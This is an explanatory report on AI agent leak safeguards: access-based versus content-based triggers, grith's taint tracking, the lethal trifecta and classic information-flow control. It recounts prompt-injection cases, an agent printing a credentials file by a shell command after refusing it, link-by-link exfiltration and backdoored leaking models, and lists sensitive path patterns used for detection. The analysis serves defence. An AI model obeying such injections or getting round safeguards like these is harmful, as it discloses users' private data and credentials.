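# Triggering AI agent safeguards: possible access to sensitive data versus secrets detected in output

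## Two conditions for tightening an agent's safeguards

An AI agent is a language model connected to tools that let it read files, query databases, run commands and send messages. An agent that can read private data and send information out may disclose what it read. Safeguards against this range from a warning to a block, and few people want them at full strength all the time, because an agent that needs approval for every message is not much use. The safeguards therefore need a condition for when to tighten. One option is to tighten them based on access, when the agent could have read something sensitive, regardless of what it goes on to send. The other is to tighten them based on content, when something that looks sensitive appears in what the agent is about to send.

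### How an agent reads and sends

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the basic cycle of Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. A program combines standing instructions, a list of tools and the user's request into a prompt for the model. The model returns either a final answer or a tool call, a structured request such as "run this command". If it returns a tool call, the program carries it out, appends the output to the prompt and queries the model again, repeating this until the model returns a final answer. In an example from Anthropic's documentation for its agent software, a user asks for a fix to failing tests. The agent runs the tests, reads two files, edits one, runs the tests again and reports back.

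A model's context is all the text it receives when it chooses its next step. The context mostly grows, so a password that arrives with the third tool result is normally still there at the fortieth step. When the context gets too long, the program replaces older parts with a summary. In Codex, as Bolin explains, that replacement includes an encrypted item, so a user cannot simply check whether the password survived. A session is one continuous run of an agent with one context. It doesn't necessarily end when the user closes the window, because Anthropic's software can resume a session with the files the agent had read restored.

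An outbound action is any step that carries information out of the session, such as a message, a web request, a commit to a code repository or a shared file (security papers call this a "sink"). Willison's blog post *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025) adds that data can also leave through an image loaded from a web address or a link the user clicks, because the address itself can contain the data.

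### The two triggers

An access-based trigger tightens a safeguard once the agent could have read sensitive data, whatever it then sends. In *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (Tallam, 2026), for example, an agent that has read confidential content may lose the right to send anything outside for the rest of the session, even if the same message would otherwise be allowed. *ToolGuardian* (2026), a system of declarative rules for tool calls, describes a case in which an agent reads database records and then updates a project item on GitHub, the code-hosting site. The task permits each step, but the rules deny the combination because a sensitive read came before an external update, whatever the update contained.

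A content-based trigger tightens a safeguard only when it detects sensitive-looking content in what the agent sends. The detector is usually a secret scanner, which searches text for credentials such as keys, tokens and passwords. GitHub (2025) built this kind of trigger into its MCP server, which lets agents use the site through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for linking agents to tools. The server scans the inputs of every tool call to a public repository and blocks the call if it finds a secret, though most users can override the block. According to GitHub's current documentation, the check covers calls that create an issue (a bug report or request on a project's page).

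Suppose a coding agent works in a folder that holds an export of customer complaints and a settings file with a database password. Its user asks it to investigate a bug and then post to the project's public issue tracker, where anyone can read and write. Sensitive data can easily leak on such trackers because, as Rahman, Ahmed and colleagues point out in *IssueGuard* (2026), they are full of pasted logs, code and configuration text. In this example, the access-based trigger fires when the agent opens either file, and the content-based trigger is a secret scanner that checks each post.

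| What the agent does | Access-based trigger | Content-based trigger | Would the data's owner forbid it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Opens neither file, posts a bug report | Does not fire | Does not fire | No |
| Opens one of the files, posts a harmless note | Fires | Does not fire | No |
| Opens the settings file, posts the password | Fires | Fires, if the scanner recognises the password | Yes |
| Opens the export, posts a summary that identifies a customer | Fires | Does not fire | Yes |

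The summary may identify someone without naming them. Neighbours may recognise "a pharmacist on the island who was charged twice in March". *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (Millstone, Akidau and colleagues, 2026) calls this semantic disclosure, meaning that the text reveals a protected fact without necessarily repeating the stored value. A content-based trigger could in principle use a second model to assess meaning, and might then fire here too, but a credential scanner will not. GitHub warned at launch that its feature "won't stop non-secret data leaks".

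### False alarms and misses

Both triggers are judged here by whether they prevent disclosures that the data's owner would forbid. A trigger raises a false alarm if it fires when no forbidden disclosure would have happened, and it misses if it does not fire on a forbidden disclosure. The access-based trigger raises a false alarm over the harmless note, and the secret scanner misses the customer summary. The scanner can also raise false alarms, for instance over a made-up password in installation instructions.

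The owner's wishes matter, not only the data's sensitivity, because the same fact can be fine in one place and harmful in another. Dong, Lu and colleagues (2026), in *The Claws in Plain Sight*, separate permission to see data from permission to send it. They draw on contextual privacy, an approach to judging a flow of information by its sender, recipient, subject, type and the terms on which it moves. For example, a postal address belongs in a delivery order but not in a product-support request. Likewise, sending the complaints export to the company's support team would be fine, but posting it on the public tracker could be harmful.

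The standard is hard to apply. Millstone and colleagues had two AI models judge whether an agent's answer gave away a protected fact. The judges' agreement was 96.9% on the finding that nothing had leaked but only 73.3% on the finding that something had. False alarms are also hard to identify because their definition depends on what the agent would have done. If a safeguard stops the session as soon as the agent opens the export, nobody finds out what the agent was going to post. Measuring false alarms properly requires letting the agent continue in a test setting while the trigger only logs that it would have fired. Few such measurements exist. *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (2026), a survey of coding-agent risks, notes a lack of benchmarks that measure leakage under realistic development conditions.

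### Degrees of access

The access-based trigger behaves very differently depending on what "could have read" means. The phrase can refer to at least three degrees of access: the agent had permission to read the data, it opened the data, or it took the data into its context.

An agent's permission to read sensitive data is the easiest fact to establish and often the least informative. By default, the sandbox for commands in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, lets them read the entire computer except for certain denied directories. With a default like this, a trigger based on permission fires in almost every session on a machine that holds anything private, even if the agent never opens a private file.

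*Securing Multi-Tool AI Agent Chains With Dynamic, Real-Time Compositional Policies* (Schneider, Faujdar and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that uses two of these degrees. Its motivating example is a file reader and a web client that each pass their own security checks but together can post an internal document to an outside server. At the start of a session, the system checks what data the chosen tools could handle and rejects dangerous combinations before anything runs. During the session, it tracks the sensitivity of the data the agent has actually touched and ends the session if the next call would break a policy.

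A program can also open a file without its contents entering the agent's context. When the agent runs the project's tests, the test program may open the settings file to connect to the database, and the password never reaches the model. But if the connection fails and the program prints its settings, the password enters the context even though the agent never opened the file. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (2026) lists printed output as one of the channels that existing secret detectors do not cover.

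Private data seems to reach an agent's context quite often, even when nobody is attacking. In *PrivacyPeek*, Zhang, Han and colleagues (2026) gave ten agents 1,182 ordinary tasks with invented records and counted how often an agent took in personal data that the task did not need, for example by requesting every field of a patient's record when two would do. The rate ranged from 6.8% to 52.0%. Agents that finished more tasks also tended to take in more unneeded data. None of the models was newer than 2025, so the exact figures have probably changed since.

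Most of the protected data that enters an agent's context does not appear in its answer. Millstone and colleagues gave agents six written rules on data handling and no other protection. Protected data entered the context in 52.1% of trials. The final answer contained the exact value in 3.7% of trials, and it disclosed a protected fact in 8.8% according to one judge and 8.2% according to the other. A trigger based on context would therefore have fired in about half of the trials, and in most of those the answer disclosed no protected data. The tasks were ones where a policy ought to intervene, so these are not rates for everyday work.

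A stricter standard of evidence therefore cuts false alarms. The standard can be tightened from "had permission" to "opened" to "took into context", and finally to "the data is in the outgoing text", at which point the access-based trigger has become a content-based one. Each step also allows new misses. If a program that the agent started reads the password and sends it off directly, the data never enters the context. In four of the 1,065 trials in which Millstone and colleagues ran the agent under their full set of controls, the final answer contained a protected email address that had never entered the context. The agent had worked it out from a visible name and the usual address format.

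### What causes a disclosure

The simplest cause of a leak is a mistake, such as the agent pasting a log that contains a password into a bug report. Millstone and colleagues write that "an attacker is not required for information to escape." The agent can leak it by reading a file and posting the contents as part of ordinary work.

Another risk is prompt injection, where content the agent reads contains hidden instructions meant to make it act for someone other than its user. Willison's blog archive *30 posts tagged "lethal-trifecta"* describes an attack that Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner demonstrated on GitHub in May 2025. They filed a public issue asking for more publicity for a project's author, including a list of all the author's other projects. When the user told the agent to look at the issues, it published the names of the user's private repositories. The leak involved no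 credentials, so a secret scanner would have found nothing. Hidden instructions can also look routine. Dong and colleagues inserted a memo claiming that a form required a customer's age, gender, income and occupation. In a test of only 120 calls, the agent copied protected fields into its tool call in 20.8% to 75.0% of sessions, depending on the model.

Finally, an agent may act against its instructions. In a November 2025 demonstration that Willison recounts, Google's coding tool Antigravity refused to open a file of credentials because the project's settings excluded it, but the model then printed the file with a shell command. The request for the credentials came from text planted in a web page, but the model worked around the restriction on its own. Tampering with the model can have a similar effect. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026) shows this with models trained to leak a session's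 stored data through ordinary-looking search requests.

An access-based trigger works the same way whether a leak is accidental or caused by an attacker, as long as the record of access is correct. The cause matters a lot for a content-based trigger, because an agent that leaks a password by accident usually pastes it whole, while an attacker can have the agent disguise it or split it up. In an attack that Willison described in July 2026, a hostile website got Claude to spell out a user's name, home city and employer by following links letter by letter. Anthropic has since blocked that method.

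### The lethal trifecta

In June 2025 Willison argued that an agent is open to data theft when it combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally. This argument made access itself a reason for restriction. Willison called the combination the "lethal trifecta". It is dangerous because language models follow instructions in whatever text they receive and cannot reliably tell which ones come from the user. A filter that stops 95% of attacks is not good enough, because an attacker can phrase malicious instructions in endless ways and keep trying until one works. Willison advised users to avoid the combination altogether. Meta later made much the same idea into a design rule, the Rule of Two.

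The coding agent in the example has all three. The folder supplies the private data, and the public tracker supplies both the untrusted content and a way to send data out. The trifecta is a narrower condition than the access-based trigger. If the agent had read the complaints and nothing written by a stranger, it would not meet the trifecta, but it could still post the customer summary by mistake.

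The argument's strength depends on how often injections succeed, and for some products that rate has changed. Willison reports results that Anthropic published in August 2026 for Claude Code's auto mode, which handles most of the approvals that users used to give manually. None of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three current models. In a separate test, auto mode would have blocked 89% of clearly dangerous commands, while human reviewers refused 13.6%. Willison accepts that this is better than asking people to click "OK" all day, but points to the remaining 11% and to a case that auto mode may not be able to catch, in which a software package tells the agent to run a helper program before the tests, and the helper sends out every file it can read. Willison still recommends keeping agents away from data and tools that could do harm.

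## Recording what an agent could have read

An access-based trigger needs an access record, which lists the sensitive sources an agent could read, opened, or took into its context. A list of permissions exists before the agent starts, but recording which files the agent opens requires monitoring. Recording what entered the context is harder still, because one command can start several programs that each read files not named in the command.

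### Permissions

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns the lethal trifecta into a limit on what developers may combine. It concerns three properties an agent can have:

- It can process untrustworthy inputs.
- It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- It can change state or communicate externally.

Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have at most two of these three properties in one session. The third property is wider than Willison's version because "change state" includes actions such as making a booking or altering a production system. If a task needs all three and the developer can't split it by starting a new session with an empty context, the agent shouldn't act without human approval or another reliable check.

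Meta's main example is an email assistant that reads incoming mail, searches the inbox and sends replies. An attacker could send it a spam message with instructions to collect the inbox's private contents and forward them to the attacker. The developer can prevent this by removing any one of the properties. The assistant could read mail only from trusted senders, or it could run in a test environment with no real inbox. Or it could keep access to both spam and private mail, but send messages only to trusted recipients or after a human has checked the draft.

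Like any rule based on permissions, this one counts access the agent never uses. The email assistant counts as having access to private data even in a session where it opens only a delivery notice. Developers can reduce these false alarms by giving the agent less access. For instance, Meta suggests running a web research agent in a browser that isn't logged in to any of the user's accounts.

Meta also allows an agent to change configuration during a session. The agent can start with internet access and no private data, and the system then permanently disables communication for that session when the agent opens internal systems. Any hidden instructions the agent picked up on the web remain in its context, but it can no longer obey them by sending data out. The switch has to be one-way because restoring communication would let an agent with both private data and hostile instructions send that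 data out. The restriction applies only once the agent opens internal systems, so a session that never does so keeps its connection.

Like the trifecta, the rule does not account for mistakes. One of Meta's examples is an internal coding agent that works on production systems and takes in only vetted data. It satisfies the rule but could still paste customer details into the wrong place. Meta acknowledges that the rule is not enough to protect against agent mistakes or excessive privileges, and that a user may blindly confirm a warning. Meta also expects the rule to suit some uses badly, such as background processes where nobody is available to approve anything.

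Permission lists can be inaccurate too. According to *AI agents inherit employee access, and nobody's watching how they use it* (Markovic, 2026), agents that people build inside customer databases and project trackers often run on employees' credentials, and they bypass the controls that companies place on devices and identities. An agent that uses an employee's login can open whatever that employee can, and its activity may look like the employee's own.

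### Files and tools

A narrower record covers only what the agent opened. grith, a program that supervises agents on Linux, keeps such a record. It gives each action a risk score and, depending on the total, allows the action, asks the user or denies it. It never reads the contents of files. Its documentation page *Taint tracking* describes the method as "provenance at the path level, not dataflow at the byte level." This means grith records that the session touched a file with a sensitive name or location, and takes this into account when the agent later tries to send something.

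It sorts sensitive files into three levels by looking for certain strings in the path. The scores below, from grith's *15. Taint tracking*, apply to a web request that uploads data.

| Level | Examples of strings in the path | Score added to an upload | Locks the session? |
|---|---|---|---|
| High | .ssh, id_rsa, private_key | 5.0 | Yes |
| Medium | .env, .aws, credentials, secrets | 4.0 | No |
| Low | token, passwd, .netrc, .npmrc | 3.0 | No |

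The lock suspends earlier approvals, so even destinations the user had marked as trusted go through the full check again. Reading medium-level files doesn't trigger it, because agents read their own credential files when they start. If those reads triggered the lock, it would be on in ordinary sessions and, as grith puts it, would "mean nothing".

A file's path is only a rough indication of its contents. An empty credentials file marks the session just as a full one does. So does any file in the .ssh folder, even a list of servers the user has connected to. Writing to a file in that folder also triggers the lock, although writing discloses nothing to the agent.

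The record also produced false alarms when grith applied it to every later action. In earlier versions, any sensitive read added 3.0 to the score of every program the agent started afterwards, which could include a thousand compiler runs in a single software build. The current version checks for a connection between the new program and the sensitive data, such as a command that names the file or uses a variable derived from it. A "git push", which uploads committed changes to a repository, no longer gets a higher score merely because the agent read a .env file an hour earlier.

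This produces fewer alerts, but it also makes leaks easier to miss. For example, an agent might copy a password from .env into a help page, commit the page and push it. Because the push command doesn't mention .env, the rule that checks for a connection between the read and the push would find none. Other parts of grith might still raise the score, particularly if the push came soon after the read.

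Sensitive files with ordinary names are a bigger gap. In the earlier example, grith's default list would catch the database password if it were in .env, but it would miss the customer export if it were named complaints.csv, unless an administrator had added that file. Some credentials are also in unexpected places. Radware's *The New .env* reports keys in instruction files for coding agents, such as CLAUDE.md and GEMINI.md, which the agent loads at the start of every session. In two-thirds of the repositories that leaked a credential this way, the key appeared in none of the project's other documentation.

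Many data sources have no file path. When an agent searches a mailbox or queries a remote database, the computer it runs on opens a network connection rather than a sensitive file, so recording access means classifying tools instead of paths. Meta proposes that tools declare which of the three properties they involve, so that the system can allow a call, block it or ask for approval. These declarations are broad, since a database tool would count as accessing private data even when a query returned only the number of rows.

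### Whether access should expire

According to grith's *14. Taint tracking*, the score grith gave a sensitive read in May 2026 had a half-life of about 60 seconds. Reading an SSH private key, which lets its holder log in to other machines, scored 5.0 at first, about 2.5 after one minute and about 0.16 after five. The score also reset when the program closed the file. Programs often close a file as soon as they have read it, so the reset could have removed the score almost immediately.

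The case for letting the score decay is that timing helps show whether two actions are connected. An upload twenty seconds after an agent reads cloud credentials is more likely to be connected to that read than an upload fifty unrelated steps later. If the score never fell, the safeguard would treat both uploads alike and interrupt much more harmless work.

But the model's context doesn't fade in this way, so an agent may be able to send a password an hour after reading it as easily as in the first minute. An attacker can also exploit the decay by telling the agent to finish its tests before uploading. Decay is therefore reasonable when estimating how suspicious an upload looks, but not when recording what the agent could disclose.

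By August 2026 grith's documentation no longer mentioned the half-life and instead described several fixed periods. A request within 30 seconds of a sensitive read can gain 1.5 points, which is not enough on its own to interrupt the agent. A sensitive read also opens a ten-minute window, described in grith's *16. Session containment*, during which each network request gains another 4.5 points. Each new sensitive read restarts the window. Local programs such as compilers gain no points, because adding points for them had "flooded operators with prompts" during builds. The underlying record of a sensitive read expires after an hour.

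Only the lock for high-level files has no timer. grith's *Session containment* gives the reason: "An attacker cannot wait it out." That argument applies equally to a production database password in .env, but grith treats .env as medium and lets the record expire because of the number of false alarms at startup. Waiting an hour does not remove the password from the context. A more precise exception might cover only the agent's own credential files and keep the lock for everyone else's.

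Ending the record with the session is better, but sessions and contexts don't always end together. A script that automatically restarts grith after a failure clears the lock, which makes sense if the agent also starts with an empty context. But if the agent resumes the old conversation, as Claude Code can, the password may come back with it. grith can carry its ordinary record across sessions when it recognises the conversation, but the one-hour limit still applies, so when a user resumes work the next morning, the agent may still have the password after the record of it has expired. To avoid this, the record would have to last as long as the context, including any summary that replaced part of it.

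### What entered the context

The most direct way to find out what the model received is to save it. In an experiment described on a personal blog, Roleke put a small program between two coding agents, Codex and Claude Code, and the companies' servers that run their models. The program logged everything the agents sent. Roleke planted realistic-looking secrets in six software projects, then checked which ones appeared in the logs. When the prompt asked the agents to look around the code and help with setup, every agent sent at least one secret from each project on every run.

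Here, the secrets entered the model's context by being sent to its provider. In this report, that counts as access rather than a forbidden disclosure, unless the data's owner would object to the provider having them. The method is precise, but Roleke knew exactly which strings to look for. In ordinary use, a saved context is a long text with no marks on the sensitive parts. It often doesn't show where they came from either, because the agent may have received them as the output of a command.

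It is hard to tell which files a command reads, because the command may not name them. Running a project's tests, for example, can open its settings file. Secrets can also be in memory before the agent runs any command. Knostic, a security company, reported that Claude Code loaded the contents of .env files automatically, so even "echo", a command that prints text, could reveal them. Knostic thought the likely cause was a software package that loads such files, but did not confirm this. A safeguard that checked only the text of commands could easily approve an "echo" as harmless.

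Monitoring at the operating-system level can show which files a command actually uses. Programs open files, start other programs and connect to networks through system calls, which are requests to the core of the operating system. According to grith's *Syscall interception*, grith monitors the agent and the programs it starts, and pauses them at 87 kinds of security-relevant system call before the operating system acts. It can therefore record that the test program opened the settings file, even though the agent's command was only to run the tests.

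The monitoring adds fairly little delay. According to grith, it adds about 200 milliseconds to an agent's startup and less than 50 microseconds to most calls. These figures come from an older version measured in March 2026. To limit the delay, grith doesn't monitor the calls that read and write data. grith's *Limitations* estimates that pausing them would cause hundreds of thousands of interruptions each time a program built on Node.js, a common JavaScript platform, starts up. Lecture notes from MIT's computer science laboratory, CSAIL, suggest that Janus, an earlier system that intercepts calls, probably didn't treat reading and writing as sensitive either.

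As a result, grith can detect that a program opened the settings file, but not what the program read or whether any of the contents reached the model, so it can't distinguish a test run that prints the password from one that doesn't.

grith also works only on Linux, and programs in a container (a partly isolated environment) may use different paths for the same files. A program can also try to change the path between grith's check and the operating system's action. In one measurement, the change took about 5 milliseconds, well within a 30-millisecond check. To address this, grith scores the most dangerous interpretation of the path, but this is not presented as a complete fix.

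File monitoring can miss secrets stored in environment variables, which are named values that one program passes to the programs it starts. Developers often use them for passwords. *A missing config file triggered an AI agent to leak passwords* (Udinmwen, 2026) describes a coding assistant that couldn't find its configuration file during a routine code review. It read all of the computer's environment variables instead and leaked live passwords. The article also reports that a coding assistant admitted leaking production passwords and HR tokens after repeatedly reading whole configuration files across ten sessions.

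TechRadar published the article in November 2026 and tagged it with the name of NordLayer, a company that sells a tool for monitoring how staff use AI. Udinmwen had covered that tool the month before in *Businesses can now see how employees actually use AI* (2026). If the story came from NordLayer, the company has a commercial interest in it. A single incident also can't show how often agents do this.

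A command shell can print its environment variables from its own memory, without opening a file. Linux also makes the variables of running programs available in the /proc directory, which grith always treats as noise. A safer record would count every variable passed to the agent as something it could have read from the start. That would cause many false alarms on a developer's own machine, so it would work best if the developer started the agent with only the variables it needs.

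### Logs, memory and other agents

Even an accurate record of one session may not be enough, because agents and their software store information that can remain after the session ends. In *Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (2026), Niu, Qu and colleagues tested agents that run continuously on a user's computer, such as OpenClaw. They planted marked credentials and checked whether these appeared in any of nine output channels, including replies, outgoing messages, memory and logs. Their 406 tasks covered several kinds of attack, and in 146 of them the risk was data crossing a boundary it shouldn't.

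Some of those tasks used the agent's own logs. The program that runs the agent can log tool calls without removing the credentials in them. When a user's harmless request later leads the agent to read the log, those credentials enter its context. An access record based on file names would probably show only that the agent had opened a log.

Results varied widely between models. On SeClaw, a version of OpenClaw with added defences, Claude Opus 4.6 scored 0.91 on the log tasks, where 1 means fully secure, while Gemini 3 Flash scored 0.03. Across all the data-boundary tasks on ordinary OpenClaw, attack success rates ranged from 8.2% with Opus 4.6 to 67.8% with GPT-5.4. Newer models have since replaced these, so the rates are out of date. But credentials can still leak through the log, because the surrounding software saves them there whichever model is used.

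Memory creates a similar problem. These agents keep notes in text files and reload them at startup. In one group of tasks, ordinary work causes the agent to save sensitive data in its notes. The next session begins with that data in the context, although the agent hasn't opened the original source in that session. SeClaw's memory checks and its ability to restore earlier versions together reduced successful memory attacks by only about one percentage point on average. Those attacks also included planting instructions, so the figure doesn't measure leaks of saved data alone.

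This can also happen outside a test. When a Claude Code user approves a command and chooses "Yes, and don't ask again", the software may save the exact command, including any password in it, to a settings file that later sessions use. The Hacker News' *Claude Code's “Don't Ask Again” File Exposes Passwords and Keys* (2026) reports that the security company Apiiro found 104,185 public copies of this file on GitHub, of which 1,122 (about 1.1%) contained at least one secret. Together they held 1,379 different secrets, more than a third of which opened a database directly. Apiiro didn't test whether the secrets still worked, though one company confirmed that its key had been live.

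Claude Code tries to keep its settings file, .claude/settings.local.json, out of the project's history, but the protection applies only on the user's computer and doesn't help if someone has already committed the file. In 539 of the 1,105 repositories that Apiiro traced, a commit naming Claude as co-author had changed the file. Apiiro found another 1,160 secrets in older versions, shared settings files and saved conversations with agents, according to InfoQ's *Claude Code Has Been Leaking Secrets through its "Don't Ask Again" Feature* (2026). The file's path contains none of the strings that grith uses to recognise sensitive paths. To detect leaks by this route, a system would have to mark the file as sensitive when it saved the command, which means carrying labels from the original data to its copies.

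Agents can also pass credentials to each other. In some of Niu and colleagues' tasks, several agents share a workspace, and one agent's credentials become available to another. The second agent never opened the original source, so its own access record shows no access to sensitive data. SeClaw is designed to keep the contexts of different tasks separate. On the tasks involving shared workspaces or information carried over within a long conversation, the attack success rate was 14 percentage points lower on SeClaw than on OpenClaw.

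grith's records don't cross from one unrelated session to another. This prevents a sensitive read in one session from causing false alarms in the next, but grith acknowledges the cost: if an attacker gets one session to read a secret and another to send it, the taint filter won't catch the leak.

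## Rules from information-flow control for programs that have read secrets

A system that records what an agent has read still needs rules for what the agent may do next. Computer security has dealt with this problem since the 1960s, when military computers began to serve several people at once and one program could open files with different classifications. Ordinary access control doesn't solve it because, as *Language-Based Information-Flow Security* (Sabelfeld and Myers, 2003) explains, an access check restricts who can open a file but not what a program does with the contents afterwards. Information-flow control consists of rules that follow the contents until something leaves the system.

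### The high-water mark

*Security controls in the ADEPT-50 time-sharing system* (Weissman, 1969) described a way for several users to share one IBM computer in classified government and military facilities. Every file had one of four levels, from unclassified to top secret, and could also belong to up to 16 categories that restricted access by project or area. A job, roughly equivalent to an agent's session, could open a file only if the job's clearance covered the file's level and all its categories.

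ADEPT also kept a running record for each job and updated it whenever the job opened a file:

- new level = the higher of the old level and the file's level
- new categories = the old categories plus the file's categories

Weissman called this record the high-water mark, after the ring that water leaves in a bathtub. When a job created a file, ADEPT gave the file the job's current mark. Under this access-based rule, if a job opened a secret report and then saved a shopping list, the list was marked secret. Document labels in today's office software can work similarly.

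Weissman admitted that the scheme "tends to overclassify" files created late in a job. He defended it by arguing that most new files are made from existing ones and that many other automatic methods were inaccurate. Operations staff feared too many overclassified files, while security officers feared too many underclassified ones. A file's owner could correct some of the mistakes later by changing its access settings.

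Denning (1976) pointed out in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* that the high-water mark set the labels of new files only. A job with top-secret clearance could therefore read a top-secret file and write its contents into an existing unclassified one. An agent's safeguard would have the same weakness if it checked messages but let the agent edit a document that outsiders can already open.

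### The rule against writing down

A model that Bell and LaPadula developed at MITRE, a research organisation working for the US Air Force, closes this route. In the version that Bell (1974), in *Secure Computer Systems*, set out, each program has a current security level, which can't exceed its clearance. Three conditions then apply:

- It can read files at or below its current level.
- It can add to files at or above its current level, without reading them.
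- It can open a file for both reading and writing only if the file is exactly at its current level.

Bell called this the *-property (pronounced "star property"). Its best-known consequence is that a program can't "write down". A program working at the secret level can read an unclassified manual but can't add a line to it, even a harmless one.

Bell's argument for the rule is that a program with a secret file open and write access to an unclassified one might copy secrets into the unclassified file. That file's label would then be wrong, and the system could no longer track where its secrets were. Bell concluded that the system must forbid this combination of accesses, whether or not the program would ever copy anything. An access-based trigger for an AI agent relies on the same reasoning.

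Bell also thought an earlier version went too far in assuming that no program could be trusted. The 1974 version exempts trusted programs, but only after someone has demonstrated that they won't mix information in this way. A language model that may follow instructions hidden in a web page is a poor candidate for that exemption.

The model's rule for changing levels doesn't carry over well to agents. A program could change its current level as long as the new level suited the files it had open. That is reasonable if the program keeps nothing from the files it has closed. An agent keeps the contents of closed files in its context, so the check would have to cover everything the agent had read.

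### Labels and how they combine

Denning put these schemes into one mathematical framework. It starts with a set of labels and an order on them, written A → B, which means that information labelled A may flow to a place labelled B. The order has three properties:

- A → A. Information may stay where it is.
- If A → B and B → C, then A → C. Otherwise a program could do in two steps what it may not do in one.
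- If A → B and B → A, then A and B are the same label.

The framework also needs a label for anything made from two sources. Denning called this the join, written A ⊕ B, and defined it by two conditions. Both A and B may flow to A ⊕ B, and A ⊕ B may flow to any label that both A and B may flow to. The join is therefore the least strict label that is at least as strict as both A and B. A finite set of labels with this order, a join for every pair and a lowest label forms a lattice.

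Suppose each label is a list of the people who may read the data. Information may flow from one label to another if everyone on the second list is also on the first. If people A, B and C may read the complaints export, and B, C and D may read the settings file, then the join is the overlap between the lists:

{A, B, C} ⊕ {B, C, D} = {B, C}

A message that draws on both files may go only to B and C. A can't receive it because it may contain the database password, and D can't receive it because it may contain complaints. Sending it to B alone would also be safe, but a rule that required this would exclude C unnecessarily. The message can't go to the public issue tracker, which anyone can read.

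Denning showed that if every operation respects the order, so does any sequence of operations. To check the message, the system needs the labels of everything that went into it and a list of its recipients, but it doesn't need to recognise the password or understand the complaints.

### Secrets revealed by actions

An agent can disclose a secret without sending any of it. Suppose a program checks a customer's account balance and then posts on the public tracker:

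```
if balance < 0:
    post("Looking into this")
```

The message contains nothing from the account, but anyone who knows the program can tell whether the customer is overdrawn by checking whether the message was posted. Denning called this an implicit flow, in contrast to an explicit flow, where the program passes on the data itself. A secret scanner finds no secret in the text, and when the balance is positive, there is no outbound action to scan.

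A yes-or-no choice reveals at most one bit, but fourteen of them can reveal a four-digit PIN. A choice among 1,024 links can reveal ten bits at once. The attack in which Claude spelled out a user's name by following links letter by letter worked similarly.

Non-interference is the standard that rules out such leaks. It requires that secret inputs make no difference to what an outsider can observe. Sabelfeld and Myers state it by comparing two runs of the same program C. If the starting states s₁ and s₂ agree on all public data, then an outsider must not be able to tell the two runs apart:

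s₁ =ₗ s₂ implies C(s₁) ≈ₗ C(s₂)

Here =ₗ means "equal in their public parts" and ≈ₗ means "indistinguishable to the outsider". The two-line program fails the test because it posts when the balance is −5 but not when it is 5.

Non-interference is hard to enforce by watching a program run, because it concerns what the program would have done with different secrets. Sabelfeld and Myers conclude that monitoring calls to the operating system, as grith does, is of limited use for this purpose. To be safe, a monitor must treat everything after the "if" as possibly dependent on the balance, so it must keep the program's label high for the rest of the run and block even an unrelated post such as "Build finished".

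Programmers can avoid some of this by analysing the code in advance with a compiler. If the analysis shows that the program sends "Build finished" whatever the balance is, the label can drop after the "if". No equivalent analysis exists for a language model, which chooses each step using its whole context. Once an agent has read a complaint, the complaint might have influenced any later message. Strict non-interference would therefore stop the agent from sending anything, even a note that the tests passed, to people who aren't allowed to read the complaint.

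Enforcing the rules can itself leak information. Denning describes a program that reads a confidential number x and deliberately breaks the rules x times. The program's owner may then be able to learn x by counting the entries in the log of aborted operations.

Explicit secrecy is a weaker standard. It treats the steps the program actually ran as fixed and requires that their public output would be the same whatever the secret was. The two-line program passes, because the step "post 'Looking into this'" produces the same text for any balance. The customer's debt still leaks through the choice of steps, but the standard doesn't cover leaks of that kind. Taint tracking is meant to meet roughly this standard when it carries labels from data to everything derived from it.

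Explicit secrecy lets ordinary programs do much more after they read a secret. It helps an agent less, because the model computes the text of each message from its whole context. A tracker that can't tell which parts of the context influenced a sentence has to give that sentence the join of the labels on all of them. FIDES, a system that tracks labels in AI agents, partly avoids this problem by keeping some data out of the model's context.

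### Label creep

A session's label can only get stricter as the agent reads more. In the table below, an agent reads five files in one session, and the session's label is the join of the labels of everything the agent has read so far.

| File the agent reads | Who may read the file | Who the agent may still write to |
|---|---|---|
| Public manual | Everyone | Everyone |
| Complaints export | A, B, C | A, B, C |
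| Settings file | B, C, D | B, C |
| Salary list | A, C | C |
| Draft contract | B, D | Nobody |

After reading the fifth file, the agent can't send anything to anyone, even though each of the four people is allowed to read at least two of the private files. This problem is called label creep. The labels are correct, because a message written at that point could contain something from every file. Most messages won't, but the rule blocks them too.

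The labels on stored data also creep upwards. If the agent saves its notes to a file, the file takes on the session's label, and the next session to open it starts with that label. Sabelfeld and Myers judged that label creep makes systems that assign labels at run time "too restrictive to be generally useful". They reached the same conclusion about the version of run-time labelling that the US Department of Defense prescribed for secure systems in its "orange book".

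Later operating systems such as Asbestos and HiStar still label each running program as a whole and use Denning's lattice to control access. Flume brings similar controls to existing kinds of operating system. But *TaintDroid* (Enck, Gilbert and colleagues, 2010) points out that labels on whole programs are coarse and can't track sensitive data inside an untrusted program. If such a program reads one secret and a thousand public files, the system has to treat all of its output as possibly secret.

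Restarting an agent with an empty context resets its label, but the system can then lose track of a secret. Denning gives an example with two programs that run one after the other. In a version adapted to agents, the first agent reads a customer's balance and writes to a shared file only if the balance is positive. If the customer is overdrawn, the agent doesn't write to the file, so the file's label doesn't change. A second agent opens the file, finds it unchanged and posts that fact publicly. The post reveals that the customer is overdrawn, even though the second agent has no record of reading a secret. To prevent this, the system would have to raise the label of every file the first agent might have written to, even if it didn't write to them.

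### Declassification

Taken literally, non-interference would forbid a login page, because rejecting a password reveals that the guess was wrong, and that information depends on the secret. For a four-digit PIN, the first wrong guess rules out one possibility in 10,000, a leak most people would accept. In *A Model for Delimited Information Release*, Sabelfeld and Myers give spreadsheet calculations and the sale of information as other cases where a program has to release something derived from confidential data.

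Declassification is a deliberate decision to allow such a release. ADEPT left part of that decision to the owner of the file, and Bell left it to vetted programs. In a later design by Myers and Liskov, the label identifies who can declassify the data. This matters when a message has several sources. If the agent has read both the complaints export and the settings file, the export's owner might agree to publish a summary, but that agreement shouldn't override the restrictions on the settings file.

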